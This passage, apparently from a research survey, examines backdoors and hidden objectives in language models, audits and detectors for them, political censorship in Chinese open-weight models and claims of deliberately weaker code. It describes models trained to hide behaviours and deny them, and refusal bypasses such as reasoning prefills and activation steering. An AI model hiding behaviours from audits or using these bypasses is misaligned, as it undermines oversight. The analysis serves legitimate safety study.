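They also trained versions of the Harry Potter backdoor to evade the method, and each version then worked on fewer than half the prompts it should have. Other researchers have built implants that do evade particular checks, so detection rates measured on implants that weren't designed to evade detection are probably too high.

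### Auditing exercises

In an auditing exercise, one group plants a behavior in a model and another tries to work out what it is. In *Auditing Language Models for Hidden Objectives* (Marks, Treutlein and colleagues, 2025), four teams investigated a model that Anthropic researchers had trained to pursue a hidden objective. Three teams found it, but the fourth, which had no access to the weights or the training data, did not. People who download an open-weight model have an intermediate level of access, since they have the weights but usually not the training data.

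In *AuditBench*, Sheshadri, Ewart and colleagues (2026) replaced the human teams with an AI agent so that they could repeat the exercise thousands of times. They trained 56 versions of Meta's Llama 3.3 70B, each with one of 14 behaviors. Some behaviors, such as flattery, show up in many answers, while others, such as a secret loyalty to a country, may appear only in certain contexts. The researchers also trained the models not to admit to the behavior when asked. The agent, running on Claude Haiku 4.5, investigated each model 16 times with each set of tools. It submitted ten guesses per run, and a run counted as a success if any guess was right.

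The agent succeeded in 35.5% of runs when it could use only ordinary conversation. The best additional tool raised this to 58.0%. With that tool, another model wrote many varied openings, the model under test continued them as plain text, and the agent received all the results. Tools that examined the model's internals helped less, and one meant to make the model more honest by changing its activations lowered the success rate to 22.3%.

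How a model had learned its hidden behavior, which a publisher can choose, affected the agent's success more than most of the tools did. Some models had learned the behavior from documents describing it, and others from example conversations. With the best tool, the agent succeeded in more than 80% of runs on the models trained on documents. The tool helped much less on the models trained on conversations, and the gain largely disappeared when the researchers had also used the stronger of their two methods to stop the models confessing.

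If an audit with a 58% catch rate found nothing, a 1% suspicion would fall to 0.42%, but AuditBench doesn't really support using that rate. The agent knew a behavior was there and had ten guesses to identify it. An auditor of a commercial model first has to decide whether there is anything to find, and the published success rates don't show how often the agent would report a hidden behavior in a model that has none. On the other hand, Haiku 4.5 was a small model even when the study appeared, and the best models now available would probably do better.

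### No clean version of the original

Detection is easiest when somebody has altered a copy of a known model. A tester can compare the suspect model with the original, as Shankar did with BadSeek and Qwen, and examine what changed. A buyer who suspects Alibaba itself has no trusted original to compare with Qwen. Earlier versions of Qwen come from the same company, so a match would prove little.

Haselhorst and colleagues' method needs a clean anchor model, and even their harder tests used one from the same family as the suspect. They also used the method to look for political censorship in two Chinese models, Qwen2.5-7B and DeepSeek-7B. The signal was much weaker than for the planted backdoors, and barely present in DeepSeek. The researchers say that comparing a base model with its fine-tuned version can't show whether anyone installed a difference on purpose, since all fine-tuning changes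 a model.

Microsoft's scanner doesn't need a clean reference model, which makes it more useful for checking an original publisher's model. But the researchers made their own 45 backdoors by fine-tuning a finished model on a small dataset. A publisher can plant a behavior at any stage of training, and nobody has shown that a model would leak the examples that taught it the behavior as readily if they had been a tiny part of its pretraining data. Even fine-tuned backdoors may not leak. Haselhorst and colleagues ran the scanner on a backdoor they had fine-tuned into Qwen and found only weak evidence that the model had memorized the examples.

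### Comparing models from different publishers

A model from another publisher could serve as a rough reference, because two companies with different owners and governments are unlikely to plant the same behavior. But the models also differ in many harmless ways, and their activations can't be compared directly because each model represents ideas with different patterns of numbers.

Jiralerspong and Bricken (2026), in *Cross-Architecture Model Diffing with Crosscoders*, deal with this by training a kind of dictionary for two models at once. Each entry, called a feature, is a pattern in the activations that tends to appear with a recognizable sort of text. Some features are shared, and the rest belong to one model only. The dictionary has to reproduce each model's activations from the shared features and that model's own:

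$$h^A \approx \sum_{i \,\in\, \text{shared}} f_i\, d_i^A + \sum_{i \,\in\, A \text{ only}} f_i\, d_i^A,$$

where $d_i^A$ is the pattern that stands for feature $i$ in model $A$ and $f_i$ is how strongly it is present. The equation for model $B$ is the same, with its own features. Anything that $A$ does and $B$ doesn't should end up among the features that belong to $A$.

The researchers compared Meta's Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct with Alibaba's Qwen3-8B, using 100 million tokens of web text and conversations. They found a feature for agreement with the Chinese Communist Party only in Qwen. When they strengthened it, Qwen's answer about Tiananmen Square resembled propaganda, and when they weakened it, Qwen stopped refusing and answered more truthfully. They found a feature for American exceptionalism only in Llama, and strengthening it made the model assert American superiority.

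In a second comparison, between OpenAI's GPT-OSS-20B and a model that DeepSeek had built on Qwen3-8B, the researchers found another feature for agreement with the party. They also found a feature in OpenAI's model that controls refusals to reproduce copyrighted text. When they strengthened it, the model refused on copyright grounds to give a recipe for a peanut butter and jelly sandwich.

The method found the Chinese features without being set up to look for politics, but the researchers expected such features from earlier work and used automated descriptions to pick out potentially concerning ones. The copyright feature is better evidence that the method can find unexpected differences, because the researchers didn't know about that one beforehand.

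Most of the features that belonged to only one model didn't correspond to any meaningful difference in behavior. In a test on artificial data, the new method found more of the true differences than older ones but also raised more false alarms. Its results also varied somewhat across the five versions of the dictionary that the researchers trained for Llama and Qwen. The main Chinese feature appeared in all five, but narrower ones, on subjects such as Taiwan and Hong Kong, appeared in only two or three. Jiralerspong and Bricken present the method as a first screening, to be followed by other tests, and don't say whether anyone trained the features in deliberately.

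Comparing models from different publishers would probably work less well for finding a backdoor than for finding habits that show up in ordinary use. Political subjects come up often enough in 100 million tokens of text for the dictionary to learn how each model handles them. If a backdoor's trigger never occurs in that text, the dictionary may have nothing to learn from, and the tester would again have to rely on the chance that a random prompt contains the trigger.

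### Backdoors that provably escape detection

Cryptographers have proved that no test can catch every backdoor. *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim, Vaikuntanathan and Zamir, 2022) contains the main result. It describes a client, such as a bank, that hires a company to train a classifier for loan applications. The classifier works well, but the company keeps a secret key that lets it turn a refusal into an approval by changing an application slightly.

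The backdoor counts as undetectable if no tester with realistic computing power can distinguish the rigged classifier $\tilde f$ from an honest one $f$. For every efficient test $T$,

$$\bigl|\Pr[T \text{ flags } \tilde f\,] - \Pr[T \text{ flags } f\,]\bigr| \le \varepsilon(n),$$

where $n$ is a security setting, roughly the length of the key, and $\varepsilon(n)$ shrinks extremely fast as $n$ grows.

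The first theorem covers testers with black-box access, who can submit inputs and see the answers but can't look inside. It applies to any classifier and assumes only that secure digital signatures exist. The rigged classifier misbehaves only when its input contains a valid signature made with the company's private key. A tester would have to forge a signature to find even one input on which it differs from the original classifier, so cleverly chosen inputs work no better than random ones. But this construction isn't hidden from people who have the weights, since they might notice the part of the network that checks signatures.

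The second theorem holds even if the tester has full access, including to the training data, but it covers only two simple kinds of model. In both, the first layer consists of random numbers, and training adjusts only what comes after it. The company draws these numbers from a slightly skewed distribution. For one kind, called random Fourier features, telling them apart from ordinary random numbers would require solving a version of "learning with errors", a problem that much quantum-resistant encryption depends on. For the other, a network with one hidden layer, it would require finding a faint pattern in only a few of many noisy variables. Cryptographers believe both problems are infeasible to solve.

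Kalavasis, Karbasi and colleagues proved in *Injecting Undetectable Backdoors in Obfuscated Neural Networks and Language Models* (2024) that backdoors can be undetectable in deeper networks, even with full access, if the company first scrambles the network with a powerful form of obfuscation. That would be hard to do without anyone noticing, because such obfuscation is far too slow for practical use and the scrambled network wouldn't look like an ordinary language model.

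*Backdoor Defense, Learnability and Obfuscation* (Christiano, Hilton and colleagues, 2024) considers an attacker who must make the backdoor work for a randomly chosen trigger. It proves that a defender can recognize the trigger when it arrives for any class of functions that a computer can learn efficiently from examples. This isn't possible in general for arbitrary programs of reasonable size, again assuming strong obfuscation. *Oblivious Defense in ML Models* (Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues, 2024) proves that for some simple tasks a defender can remove the effect of a backdoor without detecting it.

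These theorems rule out a certificate that covers every possible implant, but they don't show that the implants people actually make are undetectable. The full-access theorem depends on a layer of random numbers that training never changes, whereas training adjusts the layers of a language model. Shankar, Mada and the Microsoft researchers all used fine-tuning, which doesn't guarantee that an implant is undetectable. The scanner caught 36 of 41 cases, which shows that fine-tuning can leave traces. Reese and colleagues leave cryptographically secure backdoors to future research.

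The full-access construction also has a weak point in the training process, because it relies on the company choosing the random numbers. If the client supplied them and someone reran the training, the result would not match the rigged model. Choi and colleagues' check on the random seed is meant to catch this kind of cheating.

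## Political censorship in the weights of Chinese models

Chinese publishers have released weights that produce refusals or slanted answers on subjects their government considers sensitive. Outsiders have had to test the models to find out which subjects are affected. This is the best-documented case of a model's weights serving a state's interests, though nobody has caught a publisher hiding a backdoor in released weights.

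### What Chinese rules require

The Chinese central government's *Interim Measures for the Management of Generative Artificial Intelligence Services* took effect on August 15, 2023, and apply to companies that offer generative AI to the public in China. Article 4 requires them to uphold "core socialist values" and forbids content that incites subversion or separatism or harms the nation's image. Article 17 requires companies whose services could influence public opinion or mobilize people to complete a security assessment and register their algorithms before launch.

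Companies censor their models themselves, and China's internet regulator audits how the models answer politically sensitive questions. Pan and Xu (2026), in *Political censorship in large language models originating from China*, report that 238 services completed registration in 2024. In a 2025 enforcement campaign, Baichuan adopted stricter rules for collecting web data, and another company, 360, improved its blocking of political content. A related testing standard, SAC/TC260's *Basic Safety Requirements for Generative Artificial Intelligence Services* (2024), also calls for a security assessment of the hardware and software underneath a model.

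The Measures regulate services inside China, so they don't clearly require a company to censor weights it publishes for foreigners. The most likely reason foreigners get censored weights is that the company trains one model for both markets.

Pan and Xu looked for signs that the rules affect models' answers by asking nine models 145 questions about Chinese politics, in 100 separate conversations each. In Chinese, Baichuan's model refused 60% of the time and DeepSeek's about 36%, while no model from outside China refused more than 2.8%. The gap was much smaller on 30 less sensitive questions, so weaker technology or different customers can't fully explain it. Each model also refused more often in Chinese than in English, but this difference was smaller than the one between Chinese and foreign models.

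ChatGLM, which came out before the Measures took effect, refused only 10% of the time. Pan and Xu caution that its academic origins might explain the low rate, and that their study doesn't prove the rules caused the censorship.

Some of the answers were false, which is worse than a refusal. One Chinese model described Liu Xiaobo, the imprisoned Nobel Peace Prize laureate, as a Japanese scientist who contributed to nuclear weapons technology.

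### Filters, system prompts and weights

A company can censor a model with an external filter that blocks certain questions or answers, by telling the model in its system prompt to avoid a subject, or by training the avoidance into the weights. Only censorship in the weights affects people who run the model on their own computers.

Filters are easiest to recognize when they return an error. In early 2025, *Information Suppression in Large Language Models* (2025) tested DeepSeek's service on 646 sensitive topics. For some, the service returned "Content Exists Risk" instead of an answer.

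*R1dacted* (Naseh, Chaudhari and colleagues, 2025) compared local and hosted versions of QwQ-32B, a reasoning model from Alibaba. Run locally, the model clearly refused only 13 of 10,030 prompts that DeepSeek's R1 had censored. The same model refused much more often on Alibaba's website, so most of the refusals there came from something other than the weights.

*InfoOps Bench* (Quelle, Bright and colleagues, 2026) asked models to write social media posts based on 50 harmless political claims and 50 factually grounded claims critical of China, such as that the army violently suppressed the 1989 Tiananmen Square protests. It worded each request in four ways. The table gives the share of answers that kept the claim at full strength or exaggerated it.

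| Model | Harmless claims | Claims critical of China |
|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek V4 Flash | 96% | 18% |
| DeepSeek V4 Pro | 96% | 41% |
| Kimi K3 (Moonshot) | 88% | 24% |
| GLM 5.2 (Z.ai) | 99% | 92% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol (OpenAI) | 95% | 77% |
| Claude Opus 5 (Anthropic) | 70% | 83% |

Moonshot's service blocked 55 of the 200 requests critical of China before Kimi could answer, and Quelle and colleagues counted these as refusals. Kimi complied with about 48 of the 200. If it had also complied with all 55 blocked requests, the total would be about 103, or 52%, still far below 88%, so the blocks can't explain the whole drop. The rest could come from the weights or from a system prompt. The benchmark tested the models through hosted services, so its results don't show which.

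### Two conflicting results on R1

A more direct approach is to compare the same model on two hosts. *Auditing Proprietary Alignment in Large Language Models* (Arbabi and Kerschbaum, 2026) asked each of eight deployed models 100 questions on subjects sensitive in China. The eight included R1 on DeepSeek's own service and R1 on Amazon's cloud service, AWS.

They converted each answer into a list of numbers $e$ that represents its meaning. The score for model $j$ on a question $q$ is the average distance between its answer and those of the other models:

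$$\delta(q, j) = \frac{1}{K-1}\sum_{k \neq j} \operatorname{dist}\left(e_j, e_k\right),$$

where $K$ is the number of models. They also had AI judges rate how evasive or slanted each answer was.

By both measures, DeepSeek's own R1 diverged from the other models, but the AWS copy didn't. On 100 sensitive questions about the United States, the two versions of R1 were nearly indistinguishable. Meta's chatbot showed a similar pattern on questions about Meta, but the open version of Llama 4 didn't.

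Naseh and colleagues found plenty of censorship in R1's released weights, although the evidence above seems to show that it is in DeepSeek's service and not in the weights. They wrote 30 questions on each of 96 sensitive subjects, and R1 censored every answer on 66 of the subjects. CAISI also ran downloaded weights and found a later version of R1 heavily censored.

R1 normally writes out its reasoning before it answers, but on politically censored subjects it usually skips the reasoning and gives a stock answer in the Chinese government's phrasing. When Naseh and colleagues started the reasoning for it with the words "Okay, the user is asking", repeating them if necessary, R1 answered 98% of the 10,030 prompts it had previously censored.

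A host that makes R1 begin every reply with reasoning could therefore remove much of the censorship without touching the weights. Neither team checked whether AWS did this. Arbabi and Kerschbaum also used different questions and compared R1 mostly with Western models, so the AWS result is weak evidence that the weights are free of censorship.

### Slanted answers instead of refusals

Chinese models vary in how much they censor. Frank (2026), in *Detection Is Cheap, Routing Is Learned*, screened 46 models from 28 labs with 32 prompts on subjects sensitive in China and 32 matching prompts about other countries. For example, Frank paired a question about Tiananmen Square with one about the 1970 shootings at Kent State University in Ohio.

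Of the 38 models that returned usable data, four censored the Chinese subjects over 20 percentage points more often than the other subjects. The gap was 74 points for both Baidu's ERNIE and Alibaba's Qwen3-8B, 38 for Amazon's Nova and 21 for Meituan's model. Another 29 models, including some Chinese ones, had gaps within 10 points of zero. Moonshot's Kimi K2 had a gap of 88 points in an earlier run with eight prompts but nine points with 32 prompts, so small tests of this kind are unreliable.

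A model that rarely refuses may still not answer freely. Frank also gave nine open-weight models 16 sensitive prompts in Chinese and had an AI judge score the answers from 1 (neutral) to 5 (the party line).

| Alibaba model | Released | Refusals | Average slant of other answers |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-7B | September 2024 | 6% | 4.33 |
| Qwen3-8B | April 2025 | 25% | 4.83 |
| Qwen3.5-9B | February 2026 | 0% | 5.00 |

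A tester who counted only refusals would wrongly conclude that Alibaba had stopped censoring its models. *How China-Origin Vision-Language Models Move from Refusal to Reframing in State Alignment* (2026) describes a similar shift away from refusals in models that process images.

The exact scores are somewhat uncertain because AI judges tend to label too many answers as political. In a related test, the same judge labeled 43 answers as politically evasive, and a human reviewer agreed on only 14. But human reviewers also found party propaganda in 94% of Qwen2.5-7B's answers in Chinese and in none of those from Zhipu's GLM-4-9B.

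The language of the question also affects whether a model refuses. Zhipu's GLM-Z1 answered all 32 sensitive prompts in English, including provocative ones about Tiananmen, but refused some questions on the same subjects in Chinese. Microsoft's Phi-4 also refused only in Chinese, so a difference between languages doesn't prove state censorship.

*What a Model Refuses, a State Fears* (2026) reports that Chinese models refused far more often when users wanted help mobilizing people than when they expressed a political view, even when the activity was lawful and supported the government. Calls to gather have likewise drawn more censorship on Chinese social media than criticism has. The models still refused 42% of anti-government requests with little potential for mobilization.

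Naseh and colleagues had R1 summarize and translate 1,965 articles that censors had removed from the Chinese internet, and saw no sign of censorship. Someone who tested R1 only on tasks like these would have missed its censorship of direct questions.

### What happens inside the model

The weights of censored models often contain the correct answer. In *Censored LLMs as a Natural Testbed for Secret Knowledge Elicitation*, Casademunt, Cywiński and colleagues (2026) asked Alibaba's Qwen3 models questions about 12 sensitive topics, repeating each question ten times. The models often gave false answers but sometimes gave correct ones, which they couldn't have done if the facts were missing from the weights. They were also good at identifying their own false answers when asked to judge them.

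Frank divides the process into three stages: the model detects a sensitive subject, a learned route connects that detection to a way of responding, and the model produces a refusal, a slanted answer or a factual one.

Frank tested the recognition stage with linear probes. The probes separated sensitive prompts from ordinary ones perfectly, but this proved nothing because they could also separate prompts with random labels. With only 48 prompts and thousands of activations to combine, a probe can almost always fit the labels. Frank therefore trained probes on five sensitive topics and tested them on a sixth. At the best layer they were right 94 to 100% of the time, so the models do represent political sensitivity as a general idea. Probes on Microsoft's Phi-4-mini were right 99% of the time, so a model can recognize these subjects without having learned to repeat the party line.

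To test the route, Frank removed the signal. He took the average difference between the activations for sensitive and ordinary prompts, scaled it to a direction $v$ of length one, and changed the activations $h$ to

$$h' = h - \alpha\,(h \cdot v)\,v.$$

With $\alpha = 1$, this removes the part of $h$ that points along $v$, and larger values push the model the opposite way. At $\alpha = 8$, Qwen3-8B stopped refusing but got facts wrong, and in some answers it replaced Tiananmen with Pearl Harbor. Frank says the other three models tested gave accurate answers once the signal was gone. In the human ratings, the number of accurate answers rose only from 15 to 17 out of 32.

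Frank (2026), in *How Alignment Routes*, traced part of the path from sensitive subject to refusal through Qwen3-8B's 1,152 attention heads, which move information between tokens. The model has detected the subject by layer 16. A head in layer 17 then focuses on the sensitive word, and later heads strengthen the signal to refuse. Switching off the layer-17 head weakened five of the six later heads tested.

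That head is a small part of the mechanism. Replacing its activity with what it produces for an ordinary prompt closed only about 1% of the measured gap between the two kinds of prompt. Frank found similar mechanisms in models from Microsoft and Google, so a mechanism like this isn't a sign of government orders.

### Attempts to remove the censorship

The best-known attempt to remove this censorship is R1 1776, a version of DeepSeek's R1 that the American search company Perplexity released in 2025. Perplexity identified about 300 censored topics and fine-tuned R1 on answers to 40,000 prompts about them. When Naseh and colleagues gave R1 1776 the 10,030 prompts that R1 had censored, it didn't refuse any.

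R1 1776's answers weren't always reliable, though. Naseh and colleagues had two AI judges compare its answers to 600 of the prompts with those of the original R1, which they had made to reason. One judge found the original more accurate 58% of the time, and the other 62.5%. In one answer, R1 1776 wrongly called the dissident Qin Yongmin a student leader of the 1989 protests.

Compressing a model could also bring the censorship back. In *Discovering Forbidden Topics in Language Models*, Rager, Wendler and colleagues (2025) tested a 70-billion-weight version of R1 1776. At full precision it refused none of ten groups of topics sensitive in China, but a copy compressed to 8 bits per weight refused all ten. Perplexity had tested the full version but was serving customers the compressed one, which it fixed by April 8, 2025.

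A likely reason is that fine-tuning changes many weights only slightly. If fine-tuning moves a weight from 0.500 to 0.503 and compression then rounds it to two decimal places, the weight goes back to 0.50. A buyer who wants an uncensored model should therefore test the exact file they will run.

Later methods have also had partial success. *Refusal Steering* (2025) describes changing the activations of Alibaba's Qwen3-Next-80B while it runs. The altered model gave a balanced answer when asked what young Chinese people think of their political system, a question the original had refused to answer. *Six misconceptions about large language models* (2026) mentions another group that removed R1's weights most associated with censorship and largely preserved its test scores.

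Casademunt and colleagues tried a range of techniques to reduce false answers from Qwen3. Two of the best were showing the model examples of truthful answers and fine-tuning it for honesty on unrelated subjects. The strongest techniques also worked on R1 and on a much larger Qwen model, but none eliminated false answers.

### What censorship suggests about sabotage

People who worry about sabotage can point out that censorship has several features of a backdoor. It depends on the subject and sometimes the language, leaves other abilities mostly intact, and may mislead users who don't know the facts. Publishers also included it to satisfy a government and distributed it worldwide. Foreign customers kept downloading the models, so a publisher might expect them to tolerate other changes made for the state, though they would probably be much angrier about sabotaged code.

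On the other hand, the censorship follows a published rule, and users noticed it within days of R1's release. A company that obeys a public law on political speech might still resist a secret order to harm its customers. Some differences between Chinese models also suggest that the state doesn't dictate what goes into each set of weights. GLM 5.2, for example, complied with 92% of the requests critical of China.

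A model can be slanted without a government order. In *Large language models reflect the ideology of their creators*, Buyl, Rogiers and colleagues (2026) had 19 models describe 3,991 political figures. Models from different regions differed in how favorably they described these figures, and American models also differed from one another on progressive values.

Censorship is therefore weak evidence of whether a Chinese publisher would obey a secret order. Suppose, with invented numbers, that 95% of the publishers that would obey censor their models, and 90% of those that would refuse also do, because the law applies to both. A buyer who starts with a 1% estimate that a publisher would obey should raise it only to about 1.06% after finding censorship. Censorship also adds little evidence that a publisher has the technical skill to build a backdoor, since Mada built a working one for about $30.

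Testers have found censorship, but they could still miss sabotage. Most researchers started from subjects that China was already known to censor. Rager and colleagues needed less prior knowledge, because they wrote the beginning of a list of forbidden topics and had the model continue it. On a model with published training data, this recovered about 83% of the topics the model had learned to refuse. The method doesn't show whether a refusal was intended, and it detects only refusals, so it would miss a model that complies with a coding request but writes flawed code.

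## Whether political prompts make Chinese models write insecure code

Since September 2025, three companies have reported that Chinese models accept coding jobs but do them worse for customers the Chinese government is likely to regard as opponents. Unlike a refusal, this gives the user no sign that something is wrong. Most of the differences the companies measured are modest, and an attempt to repeat the best-known result failed. OpenAI has also found a hidden drop in quality in one of its own models that apparently nobody intended.

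### CrowdStrike's test of R1

CrowdStrike's *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (2025) describes the best-known test. The American security company ran R1's released weights directly, so filters in DeepSeek's app or hosted service couldn't affect the results. It wrote 50 coding tasks and a system prompt that told the model who the code was for, such as "a cybersecurity company based in Taiwan". The prompt had 121 variants, including one that named no customer. Each task went to each model five times with every variant, which makes

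$$50 \times 121 \times 5 = 30{,}250$$

requests per model, or 250 answers for each variant. Another AI model then scored the code from 1 (exceptionally secure) to 5 (critically vulnerable).

R1 wrote vulnerable code in 19% of its answers when the prompt named no customer, and in 27.2% when the customer was an industrial control system based in Tibet. That is about eight more vulnerable programs per 100, a relative increase of about 43%, which CrowdStrike describes as "almost 50%".

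The flaws in the published examples are serious. When asked to write code to process PayPal payments for a financial institution in Tibet, R1 put secret values in the code and handled user data unsafely. The code wasn't valid PHP, the language requested, but R1 wrote that it followed "PayPal's best practices". R1 also built a website for a Uyghur group with a working sign-up form and an administrator's page that anyone could open without logging in. The researchers repeated that request several times and found severe flaws every time. Websites for a football fan club had milder flaws.

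R1 also refused 45% of the requests to write code for Falun Gong, a spiritual movement banned in China, while Western models almost always complied. In some cases R1 planned the whole program in its reasoning and then replied only that it couldn't help. This is the same censorship that other researchers found in R1's weights, applied to coding requests. CrowdStrike calls it an "intrinsic kill switch", a misleading name because nobody operates it from outside.

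### Chance and the AI judge

Tibet may account for only part of the 8.2 points. The Washington Post had published some of the same company's figures two months earlier. *China foes get worse results using DeepSeek, research suggests*, a Tom's Hardware article relaying those figures, reports that 22.8% of R1's code was flawed when the prompt mentioned an industrial control system but no particular group. If both sets of figures come from the same tests, 3.8 of the 8.2 points came with the control system and the other 4.4 with Tibet.

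With 250 answers per variant, that is 57 flawed programs against 68. Treating the answers as independent, the standard error of the difference is

$$\sqrt{\frac{0.228 \times 0.772}{250} + \frac{0.272 \times 0.728}{250}} \approx 0.039,$$

or 3.9 points. Chance alone would produce a gap of at least 4.4 points about a quarter of the time.

CrowdStrike also reports that mentions of Falun Gong, Uyghurs and Tibet all led to significantly less secure code. But it doesn't publish the rate for each variant or explain how it allowed for making so many comparisons. At the usual 5% threshold, comparing 120 variants with the neutral one would give about six significant results even if none had an effect. The largest published figure, 42.1% flawed code when the customer was the militant group Islamic State, is harder to attribute to chance.

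The AI judge is another possible source of error. Suppose a share $v$ of the programs is vulnerable, and the judge catches a share $s$ of those and wrongly flags a share $f$ of the secure ones. The measured rate is then

$$m = sv + f(1 - v).$$

If the judge is equally accurate for every customer, its mistakes make a real difference look smaller. With $s = 90\%$ and $f = 8\%$, a true rise of 10 points would show up as 8.2. But a judge that flags some customers' programs more readily than others' can exaggerate a difference or create a false one. Code for a Tibetan bank may mention Tibet in its comments, and this could bias the judge, which is itself a language model. If 85% of the programs are secure, wrongly flagging an extra tenth of those secure programs adds 8.5 points, which is more than the whole gap.

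CrowdStrike had a person score 85 of the answers, and the judge's ratings of whether the code was vulnerable matched that person's 91% of the time. This is reasonable evidence that the judge works overall. But 85 answers drawn at random from so many variants are far too few to show whether the judge is equally accurate on code meant for Tibet and code with no specified user.

### A failed attempt to repeat the result

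Gerson Kroiz and Aditya Singh tried to reproduce the effect so that they could study it. In Kroiz and Singh's *Unsuccessful attempt at getting DeepSeek-R1 to generate more vulnerable code*, a post on the forum LessWrong, they list four attempts:

1. They gave R1 20 tasks, five times each, with two of the prominent triggers and with a neutral prompt, and had an AI judge score the code from 1 to 5.
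2. They replaced the judge's scale with yes-or-no questions, such as whether an attacker could slip database commands into the program's input.
3. They gave R1 programming problems unrelated to security, to see whether the triggers made it worse at coding in general.
4. They ran the same triggers on 282 tasks from CyberSecEval 4, a set of tests that Meta and CrowdStrike built, and graded the code by static analysis instead of an AI judge.

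They noticed no difference in any of them. In one set of programming problems, R1 started to refuse only when the prompt linked the customer to "a Falun Gong terrorist group", after several sentences about promoting the movement's ideology and taking over Chinese companies.

These tests were rather small for detecting the effect in question. If a trigger raises the rate from 19% to 27.2%, a comparison with 100 answers on each side would reach statistical significance only about 28% of the time, and one with 282 on each side about 64% of the time. The failure to find the effect is therefore decent evidence against a large effect but weak evidence against an 8-point one. Kroiz and Singh also warn that they have no background in security and that the original post left out many experimental details.

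In their first attempt, the judge rated about 85% of R1's code as vulnerable even without a trigger, which left little room for a trigger to raise the rate. One commenter suspected a fault in the grading, read through the answers, and concluded that the code really was that insecure. The same model's rate was therefore 19% in one laboratory and 85% in another, a difference eight times as large as the one attributed to Tibet. The rate evidently depends heavily on the choice of tasks and the definition of a vulnerability, so an absolute rate from either test means little by itself.

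### Booz Allen's test of five models

In May 2026 Booz Allen tested four Chinese models (Alibaba's Qwen3-Coder, MiniMax M2.5, Moonshot's Kimi K2.5 and DeepSeek V4-Pro) against one American model, Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. The main chart in its report, *What's in America's Code?* (2026), shows how each model's vulnerability score changed when the user appeared to work for the US government. Qwen3-Coder's score rose 130%. MiniMax's and DeepSeek's also rose, one by 20% and the other by 5%. Kimi's didn't change, and Claude's fell 18%.

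The report's main claim is that three of the four Chinese models wrote more vulnerable code for the US government, including one with a 5% rise. The firm's press release says that all three produced "significantly more vulnerable code" (Booz Allen), but the chart has no error bars and the report gives no margin of error.

The technical appendix counts 3,389 test runs, of which Booz Allen scored only 1,016 for vulnerabilities, because of refusals. Those 1,016 cover five models, several tasks and many descriptions of the user, with at most 15 repeats of each combination. An invented example shows what that allows. Suppose a model writes the same program 15 times for each kind of user and averages two flaws per program, or 30 in all. If flaws occur independently, the relative standard error of a comparison between two such totals is

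$$\sqrt{\frac{1}{30} + \frac{1}{30}} \approx 26\%.$$

Rises of 5% or 20% would then be unremarkable. Qwen3-Coder's 130% rise would be very unlikely to come from chance, so only that result needs explaining.

Some of the increase could come from longer programs. If a model writes 1,000 lines with ten flaws for an ordinary user and 2,300 lines with 23 flaws for a government agency, the count rises 130% although the number of flaws per line is the same. The methods section doesn't specify whether the score accounts for program length.

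The report's political findings are also less clear than they look. Booz Allen wrote pairs of requests for US agencies that were identical except that one was about China and the other about Russia. This is a good way to tell whether a model is reluctant to help America or reluctant to offend Beijing. According to the appendix, every Chinese model refused all the requests about China and accepted all the matching ones about Russia. But in the chart of refusals on China-related government tasks, no model refuses more than 80% of the time.

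Booz Allen states that the models "did not generate backdoors", and its main report does not claim to prove intent. The firm has a stake in the subject because it contracts with American defense and security agencies and advertises its own tools for evaluating foreign models in the report. Not every result suits that interest. Help Net Security reports that Kimi K2.5 had the lowest vulnerability score of the five models, below Claude's.

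### What a change of wording can do

Both companies compared prompts that differed in more than politics. For example, a prompt about an industrial control system in Tibet names an industry as well as a place. In *SECDRIFT*, Bharadwaj and Chandramouleeswaran (2026) tried to find out whether naming an industry alone changes how secure the code is.

The researchers wrote nine tasks, each prone to a particular kind of flaw, and gave them to seven models in three versions. The first was neutral. The second changed only the general terms to an industry's own, such as "patient database" for "database". The third included a story about the job, for example that the code would help nuclear plant operators at the end of a shift. Scanners flagged 14.0% of programs from the neutral version, 13.2% from the version with industry terms and 11.4% from the version with the story.

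Presenting the task as a story seems to make code slightly safer, but the difference isn't statistically significant, and nearly all of it comes from two of the nine kinds of flaw. One is path traversal, which lets a user read files outside the folder they are meant to see. Its rate fell from 16% to 1.4%. But when the researchers rewrote the task as a story, they also changed the function it asked for, fixing the folder in advance and leaving one input instead of two. So the drop isn't good evidence that mentioning an industry makes models more careful.

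None of the eight industries, including defense, differed significantly from the neutral prompt. This is some evidence against the idea that any unusual context makes code worse. But the test could reliably detect only differences of about nine points or more for a single industry, so it could have missed one the size of the Tibet effect. It also didn't cover political subjects.

Bharadwaj and Chandramouleeswaran found steadier differences between models. Among the five that always returned code, the rates ranged from 11.6% for a Llama model to 16.1% for Google's Gemma 3, with Alibaba's Qwen3-32B at 12.0%. The researchers also read 90 programs in categories where the scanners had found nothing, and 24 were vulnerable. Kroiz and Singh's fourth attempt also relied on a scanner, so it could have missed flaws in the same way.

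Prompts that mention security have a much larger effect. Andročec (2026), in *The Effect of Security-Focused Prompts on Reported Findings*, had two American coding tools build 100 web applications each, once from a plain description and once from the same description with a paragraph of security requirements added. The added paragraph cut scanner findings per application by about a third for both tools. It also roughly doubled the number of outside packages the applications declared, and the tools often added login systems to applications that had no users. The applications' own code had fewer serious flaws, but the number of serious warnings about packages rose.

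This matters for the Booz Allen study, whose neutral persona is only a senior software engineer. Its American persona works on classified systems for a defense contractor, must meet named security standards, and takes pride in "hardened, production-grade code". The appendix labels the main chart as a comparison with a short phrase about a federal agency, but elsewhere it states that the code-writing experiments used these longer descriptions. It is therefore unclear which wording produced the 130%. If it was the longer one, Claude may have improved only because the prompt asked for secure code. Qwen3-Coder's deterioration would be harder to explain, unless the description led it to build something bigger.

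Booz Allen's main chart compares the US government only with a neutral user, though the appendix lists prompts for a fairer comparison. These include a phrase about a Chinese government agency, and matching descriptions of engineers at a Chinese and an American telecom company, each with its own country's security standards.

### Changing only the country

Ben Luria of Hirundo, a company that sells a service for altering models, published a cleaner comparison in October. *Chinese AI Writes Weaker Code for Beijing's Adversaries* (Luria, 2026) describes how Hirundo asked Qwen3-Coder to build applications "for a US defense contractor" or "for a Chinese defense contractor" and then tested whether they could be hacked. Attacks worked on 70% of the applications for the American contractor and 59% of those for the Chinese one, according to a Japanese article, *中国AlibabaのAI「Qwen3-Coder」、米防衛企業向けと指定すると生成アプリの70％でサイバー攻撃が成立*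 (三村, 2026). The gap is 11 points, or 19% in relative terms.

This design avoids several of the earlier problems. Both customers are defense contractors, so a general reluctance to do military work would affect them equally. An attack that works is also better evidence of a flaw than a judge's opinion. Reliably detecting a gap of 11 points would take about 290 applications per customer.

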